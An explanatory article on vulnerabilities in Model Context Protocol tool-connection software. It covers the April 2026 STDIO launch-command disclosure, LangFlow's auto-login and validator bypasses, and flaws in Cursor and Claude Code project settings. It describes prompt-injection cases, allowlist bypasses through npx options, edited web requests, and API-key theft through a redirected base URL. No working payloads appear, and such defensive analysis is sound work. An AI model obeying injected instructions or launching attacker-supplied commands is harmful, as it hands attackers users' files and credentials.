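# Security vulnerabilities in the software that connects AI agents to tools

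## How agents connect to tools and where flaws enter

An AI agent is a language model combined with software that lets it take actions such as opening files, searching the web, querying a database or running a program. The model only produces text. To open a file, it writes a request in a fixed format, and ordinary programs read the request, fetch the file and pass the contents back. Like all programs, these have bugs. An attacker who finds one may gain access to whatever the agent can access, which on a developer's laptop often includes source code, passwords and the keys to company systems.

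Much of this software now follows the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic released in November 2024. A developer can write one connector for a tool and any application that supports MCP can use it, whereas without a common standard every application needs its own connector for every tool. According to the US National Security Agency's guidance paper *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), the protocol had become the de facto standard by May 2026, and its spread had outpaced work on its security.

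The Model Context Protocol (MCP) divides the work among three pieces of software. The host application is the program the user runs, such as a chat app or a coding tool. Inside it, each MCP client handles the connection to one server, so an application connected to five servers runs five clients. An MCP server is a program that offers tools and carries out the calls, often on the user's machine. The MCP project's architecture page assigns most of the security duties to the host application, which holds the full conversation, controls the connections and obtains the user's consent. Servers should receive only the information they need for their task.

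### One request from start to finish

Suppose a user has connected a chat application to the Filesystem server, a program from the MCP project that can list, read, create and move files. The user types "summarise the notes in this folder". At several points in handling this request, a program acts on something it has received without checking it. Security engineers call this trust, whether or not anyone decided to grant it.

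When the host application connects to a server, the client requests a list of tools. For each tool, the server returns a name, a description and a schema, which formally specifies the tool's arguments and their types (for instance, that `path` must be text). The host application gives all this to the model along with the user's words, so even before any tool is called, the model's choice of tool depends partly on text that the server's developer wrote. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that covers tool calls, requires clients to treat a tool's annotations, which are optional notes on how it behaves, as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. The user and the host application decide which servers to trust.

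The model then writes a tool call. Reduced to its essentials, the call for one note might look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "read_text_file",
  "arguments": { "path": "/Users/ana/Notes/monday.txt" }
}
```

Before anything happens on the disk, the host application can show the call to the user in an approval prompt, and the user can refuse it. The specification recommends this prompt but doesn't require it. The Model Context Protocol project's guide to the Filesystem server, which uses Anthropic's Claude Desktop as the host application, describes approval before every file operation. Host applications generally let users turn the prompt off, and people who see too many prompts start to approve them by reflex, according to the Coalition for Secure AI's *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Security* (2026), a paper by engineers from Anthropic, Google, IBM and other companies. When the prompt does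 appear, the protection depends on the user's ability to judge whether a file path is reasonable.

If the user agrees, the client sends the call in a message to the server, which opens the file. The server cannot see the conversation, so it cannot check whether the call reflects what the user wants. It can check the path, and its code should refuse any path outside the folders the user permitted during setup. The operating system will not block these paths, because the server runs with the permissions of the user's own account and may open any file that the user may open. Unless the server runs in a sandbox (a restricted environment for running programs), only a few lines of path-checking code prevent it from opening the user's files outside the notes folder.

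The server sends the text of the note back through the client and the host application to the model, which writes the summary. The user may never have read the note, which could contain a pasted email or come from a stranger. Its text also sits in the model's context, the body of text the model works from, next to the results of every other connected server. Maloyan and Namiot (2026), in *Breaking the Protocol*, point out that nothing in this context tracks which server a passage came from, so text from one server can influence calls to another. In their tests with models from 2024, banning any flow of data between servers cut the success rate of attacks from 61.3% to 8.7%, but it also cut the share of tasks the agents completed from 94.2% to 61.8%.

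### Starting a server: STDIO and HTTP

None of this works until the server is running. For a local server the user, or an installer, usually adds an entry to a configuration file. The entry for the notes folder might read:

```json
{
  "notes": {
    "command": "npx",
    "args": ["-y", "@modelcontextprotocol/server-filesystem", "/Users/ana/Notes"],
    "env": {}
  }
}
```

`command` names the program to start. Here it is npx, which runs JavaScript packages and downloads them first if necessary. `args` holds the arguments for that program: an option that confirms the installation automatically, the name of the package, and the folder that the server may open. `env` sets environment variables, which are named values that the new process can read. It is empty here, but it often holds secrets, such as the access key for a search service.

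According to the Model Context Protocol project's page on the STDIO transport, the application launches the server as a subprocess, and the two exchange lines of text over the server's standard input and output, the channels that any command-line program has. The application does this by running the command when it starts. The server needs no network port, so a web page cannot reach it directly. The Coalition for Secure AI strongly recommends STDIO for local servers for this reason.

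Anyone who controls the configuration entry can choose a command that runs on the user's machine before the model receives any input. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* lists malicious startup commands among the attacks on local servers. Users may never look at the entry, because Anthropic offers packages that install a local server in one click, with no file to edit by hand (Anthropic, *Getting started with local MCP servers on Claude Desktop*). The protocol's security guidance requires any client with one-click setup to show the complete command and get the user's approval before running it.

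In the HTTP transport, the server runs as an independent process, on the same machine or in a data centre, and the client sends each message as a web request to the server's address. Many clients can share one server. PortSwigger's *MCP server vulnerabilities*, a training page from a maker of security-testing software, notes that such a server is a web API (a program that answers requests over the web) and accepts requests from any client that can send them, AI or otherwise.

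For that reason the HTTP transport comes with rules of its own. Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026), the July 2026 specification, requires servers to check the Origin header, the part of a web request in which a browser names the website behind it. The check guards against DNS rebinding, a trick in which an attacker's website changes the address behind its own domain name, so that a visitor's browser ends up sending requests to the visitor's own machine. Two other protections are only recommendations: a local server should listen on the machine's internal address alone, and servers should authenticate whoever connects. A developer can therefore leave out authentication altogether and still comply with the specification. (The same revision removed sessions and the opening handshake, as Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) records, so older descriptions of MCP as a long-running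 session are out of date.)

### Prompt injection and the flaws behind it

Prompt injection is a way to deliver an attack through the model. The attacker hides instructions in content that the model will read, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. Suppose one of the notes in the folder is a meeting invitation from outside the company, and a line near the bottom tells AI assistants to also open a certain file in another folder. The model may open it. The Coalition for Secure AI attributes this weakness to the fact that trusted instructions and untrusted data reach the model as one continuous stream of tokens, the small units of text it processes, with no clear boundary between them. Safety training and filters help, but the coalition's paper calls them "not ironclad", even for capable models.

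The injection puts the attacker's words into a tool call, but the call's effect depends on the software that receives it. If the Filesystem server blocks paths outside the notes folder, the call returns an error, but a bug in the path check could let it read the file. That bug should be fixed in the server's code, where the fix works even if the model follows every injected instruction.

The Coalition for Secure AI cites a demonstration involving Supabase, a database service, in which researchers placed instructions in a customer support ticket. A coding tool that read the ticket could then expose private tables through an MCP server with direct access to the database. The coalition attributes the exposure to excessive tools and privileges. Narrower permissions would have limited the damage, but stricter checks on the format of the arguments would have done little because the server was meant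 to read tables.

Attackers can exploit other flaws without going through the model, so its resistance to manipulation doesn't protect against them. A malicious entry in a configuration file runs when the application starts. A web page that can reach a poorly secured local server can call its tools directly, and so can a script on the same network if the server accepts connections from it.

### What an attacker gains, and how the flaws are recorded

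The most serious result is command execution, in which an attacker makes a machine run commands of their choice. It is called remote command execution when the attacker does this over a network. The commands run with the privileges of the compromised program, and a local server can usually do everything the user can.

Data exfiltration means that private data leaves the system for a place the attacker can read. If the model follows a hidden instruction and copies a password into its summary, the password has reached only the user's screen (and the company that runs the model, if the model is not local). The attacker still needs a way to receive it, such as a tool that sends messages or a server that fetches web addresses.

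Persistence means the attacker's foothold survives the end of the session, a restart or even a reinstallation. *Security Best Practices* gives malware, backdoors and altered system settings as examples. In agent software, an attacker can also persist with a single write to a configuration file, which can make a program run every time the application opens. An attacker who achieves command execution can usually go on to the other two.

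Public records of such flaws use two labels. One is the CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) number, which identifies a single vulnerability in a shared catalogue so that vendors, researchers and administrators know they are discussing the same one. Software vendors and other authorised bodies assign the numbers. The first part of each number is a year, usually the one in which the identifier was reserved or published. CVE-2025-49596, for instance, is a flaw in MCP Inspector, a tool for testing servers under development, that let attackers run code remotely. The NSA paper gives version 0.14.1 as the fix.

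A CVE number is not evidence that anyone has exploited the flaw, and many real flaws don't have one. For *VIPER-MCP*, Sun, Kang and colleagues (2026) scanned 39,884 open-source repositories of MCP servers and confirmed 106 previously unknown vulnerabilities. When they wrote the paper, 67 CVE numbers had been assigned.

The severity score, from 0 to 10, comes from the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). Scores from 7.0 to 8.9 count as high, and scores of 9.0 and above as critical. Whoever scores a flaw answers a fixed set of questions about whether the attacker can work over a network, whether the attack needs unusual conditions or an account on the system, whether a user has to do something first, and how badly the attack would damage the secrecy, integrity and availability of data. The basic score does not measure how many people run the software or how likely an attack is. A vendor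 and an outside body can also score the same flaw differently. The question about user action is hard to answer for agents, because asking for a summary of a folder counts as doing something, but most people would not recognise it as a risk.

### Valid calls with harmful arguments

The Model Context Protocol specification separates two kinds of error in a tool call. A request that is malformed or names an unknown tool produces a protocol error. A well-formed request with an unacceptable value, such as a departure date in the past, produces a tool execution error, which the client should pass to the model so that the model can try again. Only the server can catch most tool execution errors, because only its developer knows which values make sense. The specification therefore requires servers to validate all tool inputs, and recommends that clients show the inputs to the user before sending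 them.

The protocol doesn't enforce that obligation. Sun and colleagues observe that MCP standardises the format of a call but doesn't enforce conditions on its meaning or limits on privilege, and that in real deployments the agent is left by default to construct safe arguments. They found all 106 of their vulnerabilities using prompts that led an agent to make a call with arguments of the correct type. The server then used those arguments to run a command, open a file or fetch a web address without an adequate check. The Coalition for Secure AI blames developers' mistaken belief that passing input through a language model makes it safe, writing that the model "transforms but doesn't sanitize" what an attacker supplies.

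In the notes folder example, the schema requires `path` to be text. The path to Monday's notes meets that requirement, and so does the path to the user's private keys. A well-formed tool call can therefore still contain unsafe arguments.

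## Launch settings that run any command: the STDIO disclosure of April 2026

On 15 April 2026, OX Security, a company that sells software-security tools, published *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers*. The report described many products in which strangers could choose a command for the machine to run, either by writing the configuration entry for a local server themselves or by getting an agent to write it. According to VentureBeat's *200,000 MCP servers expose a command execution flaw*, four researchers had worked on it since November 2025 and made more than 30 disclosures to vendors and projects before publishing.

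The researchers trace their findings to one behaviour of the official MCP SDKs, the libraries that developers use to build clients and servers. Anthropic considers the behaviour intended. The protocol moved to the Linux Foundation in December 2025, but Anthropic still maintains the SDKs, according to Tom's Hardware's *Anthropic's Model Context Protocol includes a critical remote code execution vulnerability*.

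### How a client starts a local server

Starting a server over the STDIO transport takes five steps:

1. The host application takes a command, its arguments and any environment variables from a configuration file, a web form or its own source code.
2. It hands them to the SDK. In the Python SDK they go into an object called `StdioServerParameters`.
3. The SDK asks the operating system to start the named program as a subprocess, with the permissions of the host application.
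4. The program runs.
5. The client writes an MCP message to the program's standard input and waits for a valid answer on its standard output. If none comes, the client reports an error.

If the command deletes a folder instead of starting a server, the folder is gone by the end of step 4, and the user then sees a message that the connection failed. OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* shows this with Python code and reports the same behaviour in the SDKs for other languages. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, a blog post whose author also promotes a security gateway they built, counts ten official SDKs with this behaviour.

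Developers can't reverse the order, because a client has to start a program and wait for its reply to determine whether it supports MCP. The check in step 5 would also be a poor safeguard, because a malicious program can send valid MCP replies while stealing files. A useful check would have to examine the command itself before step 3, for instance by comparing it with a list of permitted programs. The SDKs contain no such check, so the developer of each host application has to decide whether to add one.

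### Commands from the developer and commands from strangers

The missing check matters only if an untrusted person can choose the command. A developer can write the command into the program, or let the program copy it from a form:

```python
# The developer has fixed the command
StdioServerParameters(command="python", args=["notes_server.py"])

# The command comes from a form that a user fills in
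StdioServerParameters(command=form["command"], args=form["args"])
```

The fixed command lets a user start only the notes server, whereas the form lets the user start any program on the machine. This is usually harmless on a laptop, since the person filling in the form owns the machine and could type the same command into a terminal. But many agent tools are web applications that run on a server, and the people who open them in a browser should not be able to run commands on that server.

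OX Security calls the form version bad practice and complains that the SDK doesn't warn developers who write it. Libraries built on the SDK don't add a warning either. LangChain's MCP adapters and FastMCP, which many applications use instead of the SDK itself, pass the command along unchanged.

### Configuration screens open to strangers

LangFlow is an open-source tool, owned by IBM, for building agents and workflows in a browser. Its settings page has a form for adding MCP servers, which accepted a STDIO server with any command and arguments. The form was meant only for logged-in users, but LangFlow had an auto-login feature, intended to save developers from entering a password on their own machines, that issued a session token to anyone who requested one. An attacker could use a token to submit a server configuration containing a command, and LangFlow would pass the command to the SDK,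 which ran it with LangFlow's permissions.

Only the owner can request a token on a laptop that accepts no outside connections. But OX Security used Shodan, a search engine for connected devices, to find more than 915 LangFlow instances open to the internet. The researchers reported the flaw on 11 January 2026, tried repeatedly to reach the maintainers, and received a direct acknowledgement on 18 March. OX Security's *MCP Supply Chain Advisory* lists every version of LangFlow as affected and gives no CVE number.

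LiteLLM, a gateway that lets applications reach models from many companies through one interface, did require an account. But a logged-in user could add an MCP server with any command, and LiteLLM ran that command on the host without validating it (CVE-2026-30623). Anyone allowed to configure a tool could therefore take control of the machine and any model keys and other credentials it held. The maintainers fixed the flaw in version 1.83.7-stable.

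A login requirement offers less protection when anyone can create an account. Bisheng, another platform for building AI applications, also required an account before accepting a server configuration, but it let anyone register (CVE-2026-33224).

### Allowlists and the options of permitted programs

Two of the projects, Flowise and Upsonic, already had safeguards against this danger. Both are open-source tools for building agents, and both accepted only commands on an allowlist, which included common launchers such as Python, npm and npx. Flowise also stripped special characters, including some that a command shell reads as the start of a second command.

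OX Security's researchers got past both allowlists with npx, the package runner from the Filesystem server's configuration entry. npx has an option that runs a piece of text as a command. The researchers put npx in the command field, where Flowise accepted it, and put the option and a harmless test command among the arguments. Security engineers call this argument injection, meaning that a program reads a supplied value as one of its command-line options.

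Blocking that option would prevent one attack but not a broader one, in which the attacker publishes a package and has npx run it in the normal way. Python likewise runs whichever script it receives. An allowlist that checks only the program's name therefore restricts very little once it includes a package runner or a programming language. A useful allowlist would have to check the whole entry: the program, its arguments, and the exact package and version.

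Upsonic's maintainers responded to CVE-2026-30625 with a warning that users of version 0.72.0 and later see before they set up MCP tools. The allowlist bypass is still possible, according to OX Security. VentureBeat reported on 1 May 2026 that a fix for Flowise (CVE-2026-40933) had shipped, but still advised administrators to isolate the whole process instead of relying on a list of commands.

### A transport missing from the menu

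The web interface of Letta, a platform for agents with long-term memory, let users add an MCP server only by giving a web address. When the researchers read the source code, they found that the server behind the interface still accepted a third type of connection, STDIO. They clicked the button that tests a connection, intercepted their own browser's request, changed the type to STDIO and added a command, which Letta's production servers ran.

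OX Security describes this as a simulated man-in-the-middle attack, a term that normally means intercepting someone else's traffic. Here the attacker only edits a request from their own browser. They don't need to be on the victim's network, and the edit takes a few minutes with free tools.

DocsGPT, an assistant that answers questions from documents, had the same weakness in version 0.15.0 (CVE-2026-26015). Both vendors repaired their hosted services. Both also publish their code, and OX Security listed the copies people run themselves as affected too. VentureBeat reported that DocsGPT had shipped a fix by 1 May.

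### Entries that an agent writes

A coding agent can edit files on a developer's machine, including the one that lists the agent's own MCP servers. If the agent reads a web page that contains a prompt injection, it may add a server entry written by the attacker. The coding tool Windsurf ran the command in such an entry without any approval (CVE-2026-30615).

OX Security found the same basic weakness in Cursor, Claude Code, Gemini CLI and GitHub Copilot. These tools ask the user to allow the edit at least once, and their vendors do not consider an edit the user allowed to be a vulnerability. The researchers object that the user may approve the edit without knowing what it contains.

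The table below shows the fix status of the web applications and agent frameworks that the advisory names. "No fix listed" means that neither the company's publications nor VentureBeat's review of 1 May records a fix.

| Product | CVE | What the attacker needs | Versions affected | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LangFlow | none given | Network access | All at the time | Partial by May 2026 |
| LiteLLM | CVE-2026-30623 | An account | Before 1.83.7-stable | Fixed |
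| Bisheng | CVE-2026-33224 | An account, open to anyone | All at the time | Fixed |
| GPT Researcher | CVE-2025-65720 | Access to the interface, or a victim who opens a crafted web page | 3.3.7 to 3.4.4 | No fix listed |
| Agent Zero | CVE-2026-30624 | Access to the settings | All at the time | No fix listed |
| LangBot | CVE-2026-54449 | An account | Up to 4.10.0 | No fix listed |
| Fay | CVE-2026-30618 | Access to the web interface | 4.3.1 | No fix listed |
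| Jaaz | CVE-2026-30616 | Network access | All self-hosted copies | No fix listed |
| Langchain-Chatchat | CVE-2026-30617 | Network access | 0.3.1 | No fix listed |
| Flowise | CVE-2026-40933 | Access to the MCP settings | Around 3.1.0 | Fix reported |
| Upsonic | CVE-2026-30625 | Ability to define an MCP task | All | Warning only |
| DocsGPT | CVE-2026-26015 | An edited web request | 0.15.0 | Fixed |
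| Letta | none given | An account and an edited web request | All at the time | Hosted service fixed |

These are the researchers' own demonstrations. The company's publications don't report criminals using any of them.

### What the published figures measure

The researchers ran commands on six live platforms with paying customers. This is the most reliable of the headline figures because they tested the systems with the settings their operators had chosen.

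The researchers also submitted a harmless test entry to 11 registries, the online directories where people find MCP servers to install. Nine published it, including LobeHub and Cursor Directory. GitHub rejected the entry and Cline never answered, according to bdtechtalks' *The 'by design' security flaw of Model Context Protocol (MCP)*. So most registries did not review what they published. The test did not measure how many people would have installed the entry.

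Coverage of the disclosure can be confusing because the company's main report lists malicious registry entries as the last of four families of attack, while its advisory lists hidden STDIO options like Letta's fourth. These two kinds of attack have little in common technically. Someone who installs a malicious server has agreed to run the attacker's program, and checking the launch command won't help because the harm is in the program it starts.

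The widely reported figure of up to 200,000 vulnerable instances is an estimate. VentureBeat reports that the researchers found about 7,000 servers on public internet addresses with the STDIO transport active and extrapolated from that count, but doesn't say what ratio they used. flyingpenguin gives the count as 7,374, from Shodan. Nobody, therefore, observed most of the 200,000 installations. If they are behind a company firewall or on a laptop, an attacker on the internet can't reach their settings pages the way the researchers reached LangFlow's.

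Even the smaller figure needs careful interpretation, because a STDIO server opens no network port. A search engine can detect only the web application around it, and whether a stranger can add a server there depends on that application's login. Some reports left out these qualifications. bdtechtalks wrote of more than 200,000 public servers, and VentureBeat itself wrote near the end of its article that the company had documented 200,000.

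The 150 million downloads in the report's title seem to be the sum of three packages' downloads. flyingpenguin lists 73 million for the Python SDK, 57 million for LiteLLM and 22 million for FastMCP, which makes 152 million. Installing FastMCP also downloads the SDK, so a single installation can count twice, and automated build systems download the same packages repeatedly. The total is a good indication of how widely developers use this code, but it is almost no help in estimating how many machines an attacker could take over.

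### Whose job it is to check the command

The researchers contacted Anthropic on 7 January 2026. According to their report, as reproduced by flyingpenguin, Anthropic replied that launching a command is an explicit part of how STDIO servers work and wrote, "we believe that this design does represent a secure default". VentureBeat cautions that Anthropic's fuller position reached the public through OX Security, and that "expected" is the only word Anthropic itself has put on record. Anthropic didn't answer VentureBeat's request for comment.

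Nine days after the first contact, Anthropic added a note to SECURITY.md, the file that sets out a project's security policy, advising caution with STDIO adapters, but it did not change the code. The researchers told VentureBeat that this change "didn't fix anything."

Other maintainers gave similar answers. LangChain said application authors must validate untrusted input. FastMCP's maintainers said the transport starts a subprocess by design, as the specification requires. Google called the behaviour in Gemini CLI a known issue with no fix planned in the near term. According to OX Security, some vendors answered that they run the command in a sandbox, where it can't reach other customers' data. OX accepts this, but points out that an attacker could still use the vendor's computers to mine cryptocurrency or relay traffic.

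The maintainers reasonably argue that the STDIO transport exists to start local programs, so it has to accept the name of one. Someone who can edit the configuration file on a laptop can usually run commands there already, so the SDK gives that person no new power. Hirschberg (2026), in *If “stdio” is a Vulnerability, So Is “git clone”*, points out that much developer software works this way. Since about 2015, Jupyter, the notebook program that data scientists use, has started its language engines from a JSON file containing a command and environment variables, and nobody calls that a critical flaw. Hirschberg, chief technology officer of another security company, ARMO, considers the research sound but its title a marketing choice.

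The most useful comparison in that article is to Git, which runs scripts from a folder called hooks as a normal feature. In 2024 researchers found a serious vulnerability (CVE-2024-32002) that let a malicious repository write into that folder while a user was copying the repository. By the same reasoning, running a configured command is not a flaw in MCP, but a product is flawed if it lets an outsider supply the command. Most of the April cases fit this description. LangFlow gave strangers a session, and Letta accepted a transport that its menu did not offer. Each product's maintainers could fix these errors without changing the SDK.

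Hirschberg's comparison is weaker where it rates MCP's safeguards. It places MCP in the middle of a list of similar tools because MCP requires approval of each server and a restart. Desktop applications such as Claude Desktop and Cursor do require both, but LangFlow and Letta ran the command when a web request arrived, without anyone's approval.

The case for changing the SDK rests on how often developers made the same mistake. Besides the products in the table, OX Security lists separate reports by other researchers on LibreChat (CVE-2026-22252), WeKnora (CVE-2026-22688) and a package for creating STDIO servers (CVE-2025-54994). Carter Rees, a vice president at the company Reputation, told VentureBeat that an error repeated across so many independent projects "stops being a developer mistake". Flowise is especially awkward for Anthropic because its developers did what Anthropic says developers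 should do, and their filter failed at the first serious attempt.

Whether a change to the SDK would have prevented the failures depends on the change. The researchers proposed several, including a default allowlist of commands. Leaving npx off that list would break a very common way of starting a server, but including it would let the Flowise bypass work everywhere. Filtering commands would be as difficult in the SDK as it was in Flowise.

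Fixed manifests are more promising. The administrator lists the permitted servers in advance, each under a short name, and the application can start a server only by that name. A visitor to LangFlow could then choose "notes" from the list but could not type a command. This would have stopped the attacks through open forms, permitted programs and edited requests. However, users could no longer add their own servers, a feature that several of these products offer. An agent that can edit the present configuration file could also edit the manifest file unless something protected it.

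The mildest proposal is an explicit flag. Moshe Siman Tov Bustan, who leads the research team, told bdtechtalks that the SDK could block arbitrary commands by default and let developers enable them with a flag whose name states the danger. The SDK cannot distinguish a command in the source code from one entered in a web form, since both arrive as text, so it would have to require the flag for every command outside some approved set. Developers who want their users to add servers would simply set it. But reviewers and scanning tools could easily find the flag, and developers would see it while writing the risky line, when few of them read SECURITY.md.

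LangFlow would still have needed to check who was sending the request under any of these changes. A manifest or a flag would probably have prevented some of the other cases with modest effort, so it is fair to criticise Anthropic for changing only the documentation. That doesn't make the SDK's behaviour a vulnerability in the sense that LangFlow's open login was.

### LangFlow after the disclosure

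By July 2026 LangFlow had a validator that rejected new server configurations containing dangerous arguments or environment variables. A series of advisories then described ways to bypass it. IBM's *MCP Server Configuration Validator Bypass via File Upload API* (2026), dated 2 July, explains that the validator checked configurations submitted through the MCP settings but not those a logged-in user uploaded as files (CVE-2026-7755). The next time LangFlow listed its servers, it read the uploaded file and started the servers defined in it. Version 1.10.1 fixed this.

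The validator's list of forbidden environment variables was also incomplete. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-12940* (2026) records that the list omitted three variables that change how the Bash command shell behaves, which an attacker without an account could use to run code in versions up to 1.10.1. At the end of July, IBM's *Langflow is affected by security vulnerabilities in Model Context Protocol features* listed seven more flaws. These included poor validation of the command field itself (CVE-2026-17623). In another, a filter on the arguments of Docker, which runs software in isolated containers, missed some arguments that give a container access to the host's files (CVE-2026-17626, reported by Thai Son Dinh of VinSOC Labs). IBM directed users to version 1.11.0.

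Even then, an ordinary user could start any local program by adding an MCP component with the STDIO transport to a workflow. This bypassed two settings that administrators could use to prevent it, and worked in LangFlow versions up to 1.11.5, according to OffSeq's *CVE-2026-81941*. Anthropic recommends that developers filter commands in their own products, and LangFlow's developers needed several attempts to do so.

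The auto-login flaw took even longer to fix. Intruder's *CVE-2026-9103* (2026) repeats IBM's July description of the flaw, which says that LangFlow issued long-lived tokens with full administrative rights to any caller when auto-login was on, as it was by default. The entry lists version 1.10.1 as the fix. On 28 October IBM published another bulletin, covering versions 1.0.0 to 1.12.8, that described one flaw as "an incomplete remediation of an auto-login security control". Trent (2026), in *MCP as the New Attack Surface*, identifies this flaw as CVE-2026-93680 and explains that the earlier fixes shortened the life of the token but still let a caller get one without a password.

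The same bulletin lists CVE-2026-110186, which lets an attacker without an account run code. Both flaws score 9.8. The April attack used LangFlow as an MCP client by giving it a server to start. This one uses LangFlow as an MCP server, a role in which it offers its workflows as tools to other applications. In Trent's reconstruction, the attacker takes the anonymous session, lists the available tools, and uses them to create a workflow containing Python code, which LangFlow then runs. A working login would have stopped this attack, but a check on STDIO commands would not.

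Version 1.13.0, released on 22 October, fixes both flaws and turns auto-login off by default. IBM offers no workaround for older versions. According to The Hacker News' *Critical Langflow Flaws Could Let Unauthenticated Attackers Run Code on Servers* (2026), it is unclear from IBM's bulletin whether servers with auto-login already off are vulnerable, so their administrators should upgrade too. Administrators who rely on auto-login need to prepare their account for password sign-in before upgrading, or they may lock themselves out.

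On 3 November, Cornelißen (2026) wrote in *Langflow* that nobody had yet reported attacks using the October flaws, and advised replacing the access keys stored on any server that had been open to the internet. A module for Metasploit, a public toolkit for testing attacks, already used the login flaw to list a server's tools, but it did not run code on the server.

Attackers have exploited other flaws in LangFlow. At the end of October, The Hacker News reported, the US cybersecurity agency CISA listed six of them in its catalogue of vulnerabilities known to be exploited. An attack on the most recent addition, CVE-2026-9198, starts with the same anonymous administrator token that the researchers used in their demonstration, then runs Python code through a different part of the program. On 1 September, *Hackers Start Exploiting Critical Langflow Vulnerability* (Arghire, 2026) reported attacks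 on CVE-2026-0768, another flaw that can be exploited without logging in.

Version 1.13.0 is itself out of date. Intruder's *CVE-2026-127067* (2026), published on 3 December, describes an authorisation flaw that lets one logged-in user read or alter other users' data. Version 1.13.1 fixes this flaw, which is unrelated to launch commands.

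## Project files that start programs in coding agents

A project that a developer downloads can also contain launch settings. A coding agent reads, edits and runs code at the user's request, and most coding agents look for settings in the folder where the user starts them. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, reads general settings from `.claude/settings.json` and a list of MCP servers from `.mcp.json`. Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, looks in the `.cursor` folder.

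Developers usually share a project as a repository, a folder with a record of every change, and each team member works on a copy. If the repository includes the agent's settings, everyone who copies it gets the same tools, such as a server that connects to the team's test database. But anyone who can change the repository can also change those settings. *Caught in the Hook* (Donenfeld and Vanunu, 2026) says that developers tend to see these settings files as background information and rarely review them as carefully as code. Donenfeld and Vanunu work for Check Point, the security company that reported the main flaws in Cursor and Claude Code.

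A server entry contains a command, so a downloaded project that includes one can start programs on the user's machine. The main protection is a prompt for the user's approval before the programs start. This protection was inadequate in Cursor, where the prompt covered too little, and in Claude Code, where it appeared too late.

### Cursor: approval tied to a server's name

When a user opened a project with an MCP server that Cursor had not seen before, Cursor asked for approval. It remembered the answer under the server's name and never compared the command again. Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu (2025), in *CVE-2025-54136*, show how a collaborator could exploit this:

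1. The attacker adds a server with a harmless command to the shared repository.
2. A colleague opens the project, sees the prompt and approves the server.
3. The attacker changes the command but keeps the name.
4. The colleague's copy receives the change, and Cursor runs the new command without a prompt. It does so again every time the colleague opens the project.

The two versions of the entry might look like this:

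```text
Approved:  "notes": { "command": "python", "args": ["notes_server.py"] }
Later:     "notes": { "command": "(a program the attacker chose)" }
```

A careful colleague would also have approved the first version, because nothing was wrong with it. Cursor should have asked for approval again after step 3, before starting the changed command.

The attacker needs permission to change a branch (a parallel version of the project) that the victim uses, or some way to write files on the victim's machine. MITRE's *Cursor's Modification of MCP Server Definitions Bypasses Manual Re-approvals* (2025), the official record, gives the flaw a severity score of 7.2 and lists versions up to 1.2.4 as affected. Check Point reported the flaw on 16 July 2025, and Cursor fixed it in version 1.3, released on 29 July. The release notes didn't mention the flaw, but Check Point confirmed that any change to an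 entry, even an added space, now triggers the approval prompt again. In August 2025 CISA recorded no known exploitation, and Tenable, another security company, says nobody exploited the flaw before its disclosure.

### Claude Code: effects before consent

Claude Code shows a trust dialog when a user starts it in a new folder. Check Point's researchers reported three flaws in this process between July and October 2025.

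The first flaw involved hooks, which are commands that Claude Code runs at set moments, such as tidying the code after each edit. The researchers added a hook to a test project to open the calculator at the start of a session. The trust dialog mentioned running files "with your permission", and Claude Code normally asked before each command, so they expected a second prompt before the hook ran. Instead, the calculator opened as soon as they accepted the dialog. Claude Code should have shown the hook's command and asked before running it. Anthropic's fix was a dialog with a clearer warning. The Hacker News (2026) gives the fixed version as 1.0.87 and the severity score as 8.7. The flaw has no CVE number.

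The new dialog warned that commands in `.mcp.json` might run, so the researchers looked for a way to start a server without any consent. Claude Code had two settings that approved a project's servers in advance, so that each member of a team didn't have to answer the same prompt. The project itself could supply these settings, so a malicious repository could contain both a server and its approval. When the user started Claude Code in the folder, it read the settings and started the server before the user could answer the trust dialog. In the researchers' test, the calculator opened on top of the dialog.

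Claude Code could act on a project's contents before the user answered the startup trust dialog. Check Point reported this flaw (CVE-2025-59536) on 3 September 2025, and Anthropic fixed it on 22 September. MITRE's *Claude Code's startup trust dialog could lead to Command Execution attack* (2025) lists every version before 1.0.111 as affected and gives the flaw a severity score of 8.7. Since the fix, a project's servers can't start until the user approves, whatever the project's settings contain.

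The third flaw (CVE-2026-21852) exposed the user's API key, the secret that identifies the account and lets Anthropic bill it, without starting any program. A project's settings could change `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, the environment variable that sets where Claude Code sends its requests to the model. Each request includes the key, and Claude Code sent several requests while starting up. If a project had changed the address, the attacker received the key before the user could respond to the dialog asking whether to trust the folder.

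An attacker could use the key to run up charges and to reach files that the victim's colleagues had uploaded to the same workspace, a shared storage area in Anthropic's developer platform. The platform doesn't let anyone download uploaded files directly, but the researchers got around this by asking Claude to copy a file and then downloading the copy. MITRE's *Claude Code Leaks Data via Malicious Environment Configuration Before Trust Confirmation* (2026) gives the flaw a score of 5.3, which seems low for a team that shares a workspace.

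Accounts differ on how version 2.0.65 fixed the flaw. Donenfeld and Vanunu write that Claude Code now sends no requests until the user has accepted the dialog. In *TrustFall*, a May 2026 report from the security company Adversa AI, Utevsky writes that Anthropic stopped projects from changing the address at all. If only the timing changed, an attacker could still steal the key from a user who trusts a malicious project. When the records appeared, CISA listed no known exploitation of either numbered flaw.

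### Routine commands that ran before the dialog

Other researchers found more project code that ran before the user had agreed to anything. Nizry, in *Arbitrary code execution and Claude Code CLI*, logged every file that Claude Code opened and every command that it ran before the trust dialog. One was `git status`, which asks the version-control program Git what has changed in a project. Git has settings of its own in the project folder, and some of them name programs for Git to run. A malicious project could therefore use Git to start the attacker's program. (Copying a repository in the normal way doesn't copy these settings, so the attacker would have to deliver the folder differently, for example as an archive.)

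Anthropic removed `git status` from the startup sequence in version 2.0.34. Version 2.0.50 still ran five other Git commands before the dialog, and Nizry found a combination of Git settings that made one of them start a program. Two of Claude Code's own settings also ran commands before the dialog. In version 2.0.71, released by 16 December 2025, Anthropic fixed all of these by moving the risky operations to after the dialog. The `git status` flaw is older than coding agents; code editors from Microsoft and JetBrains had it in 2021.

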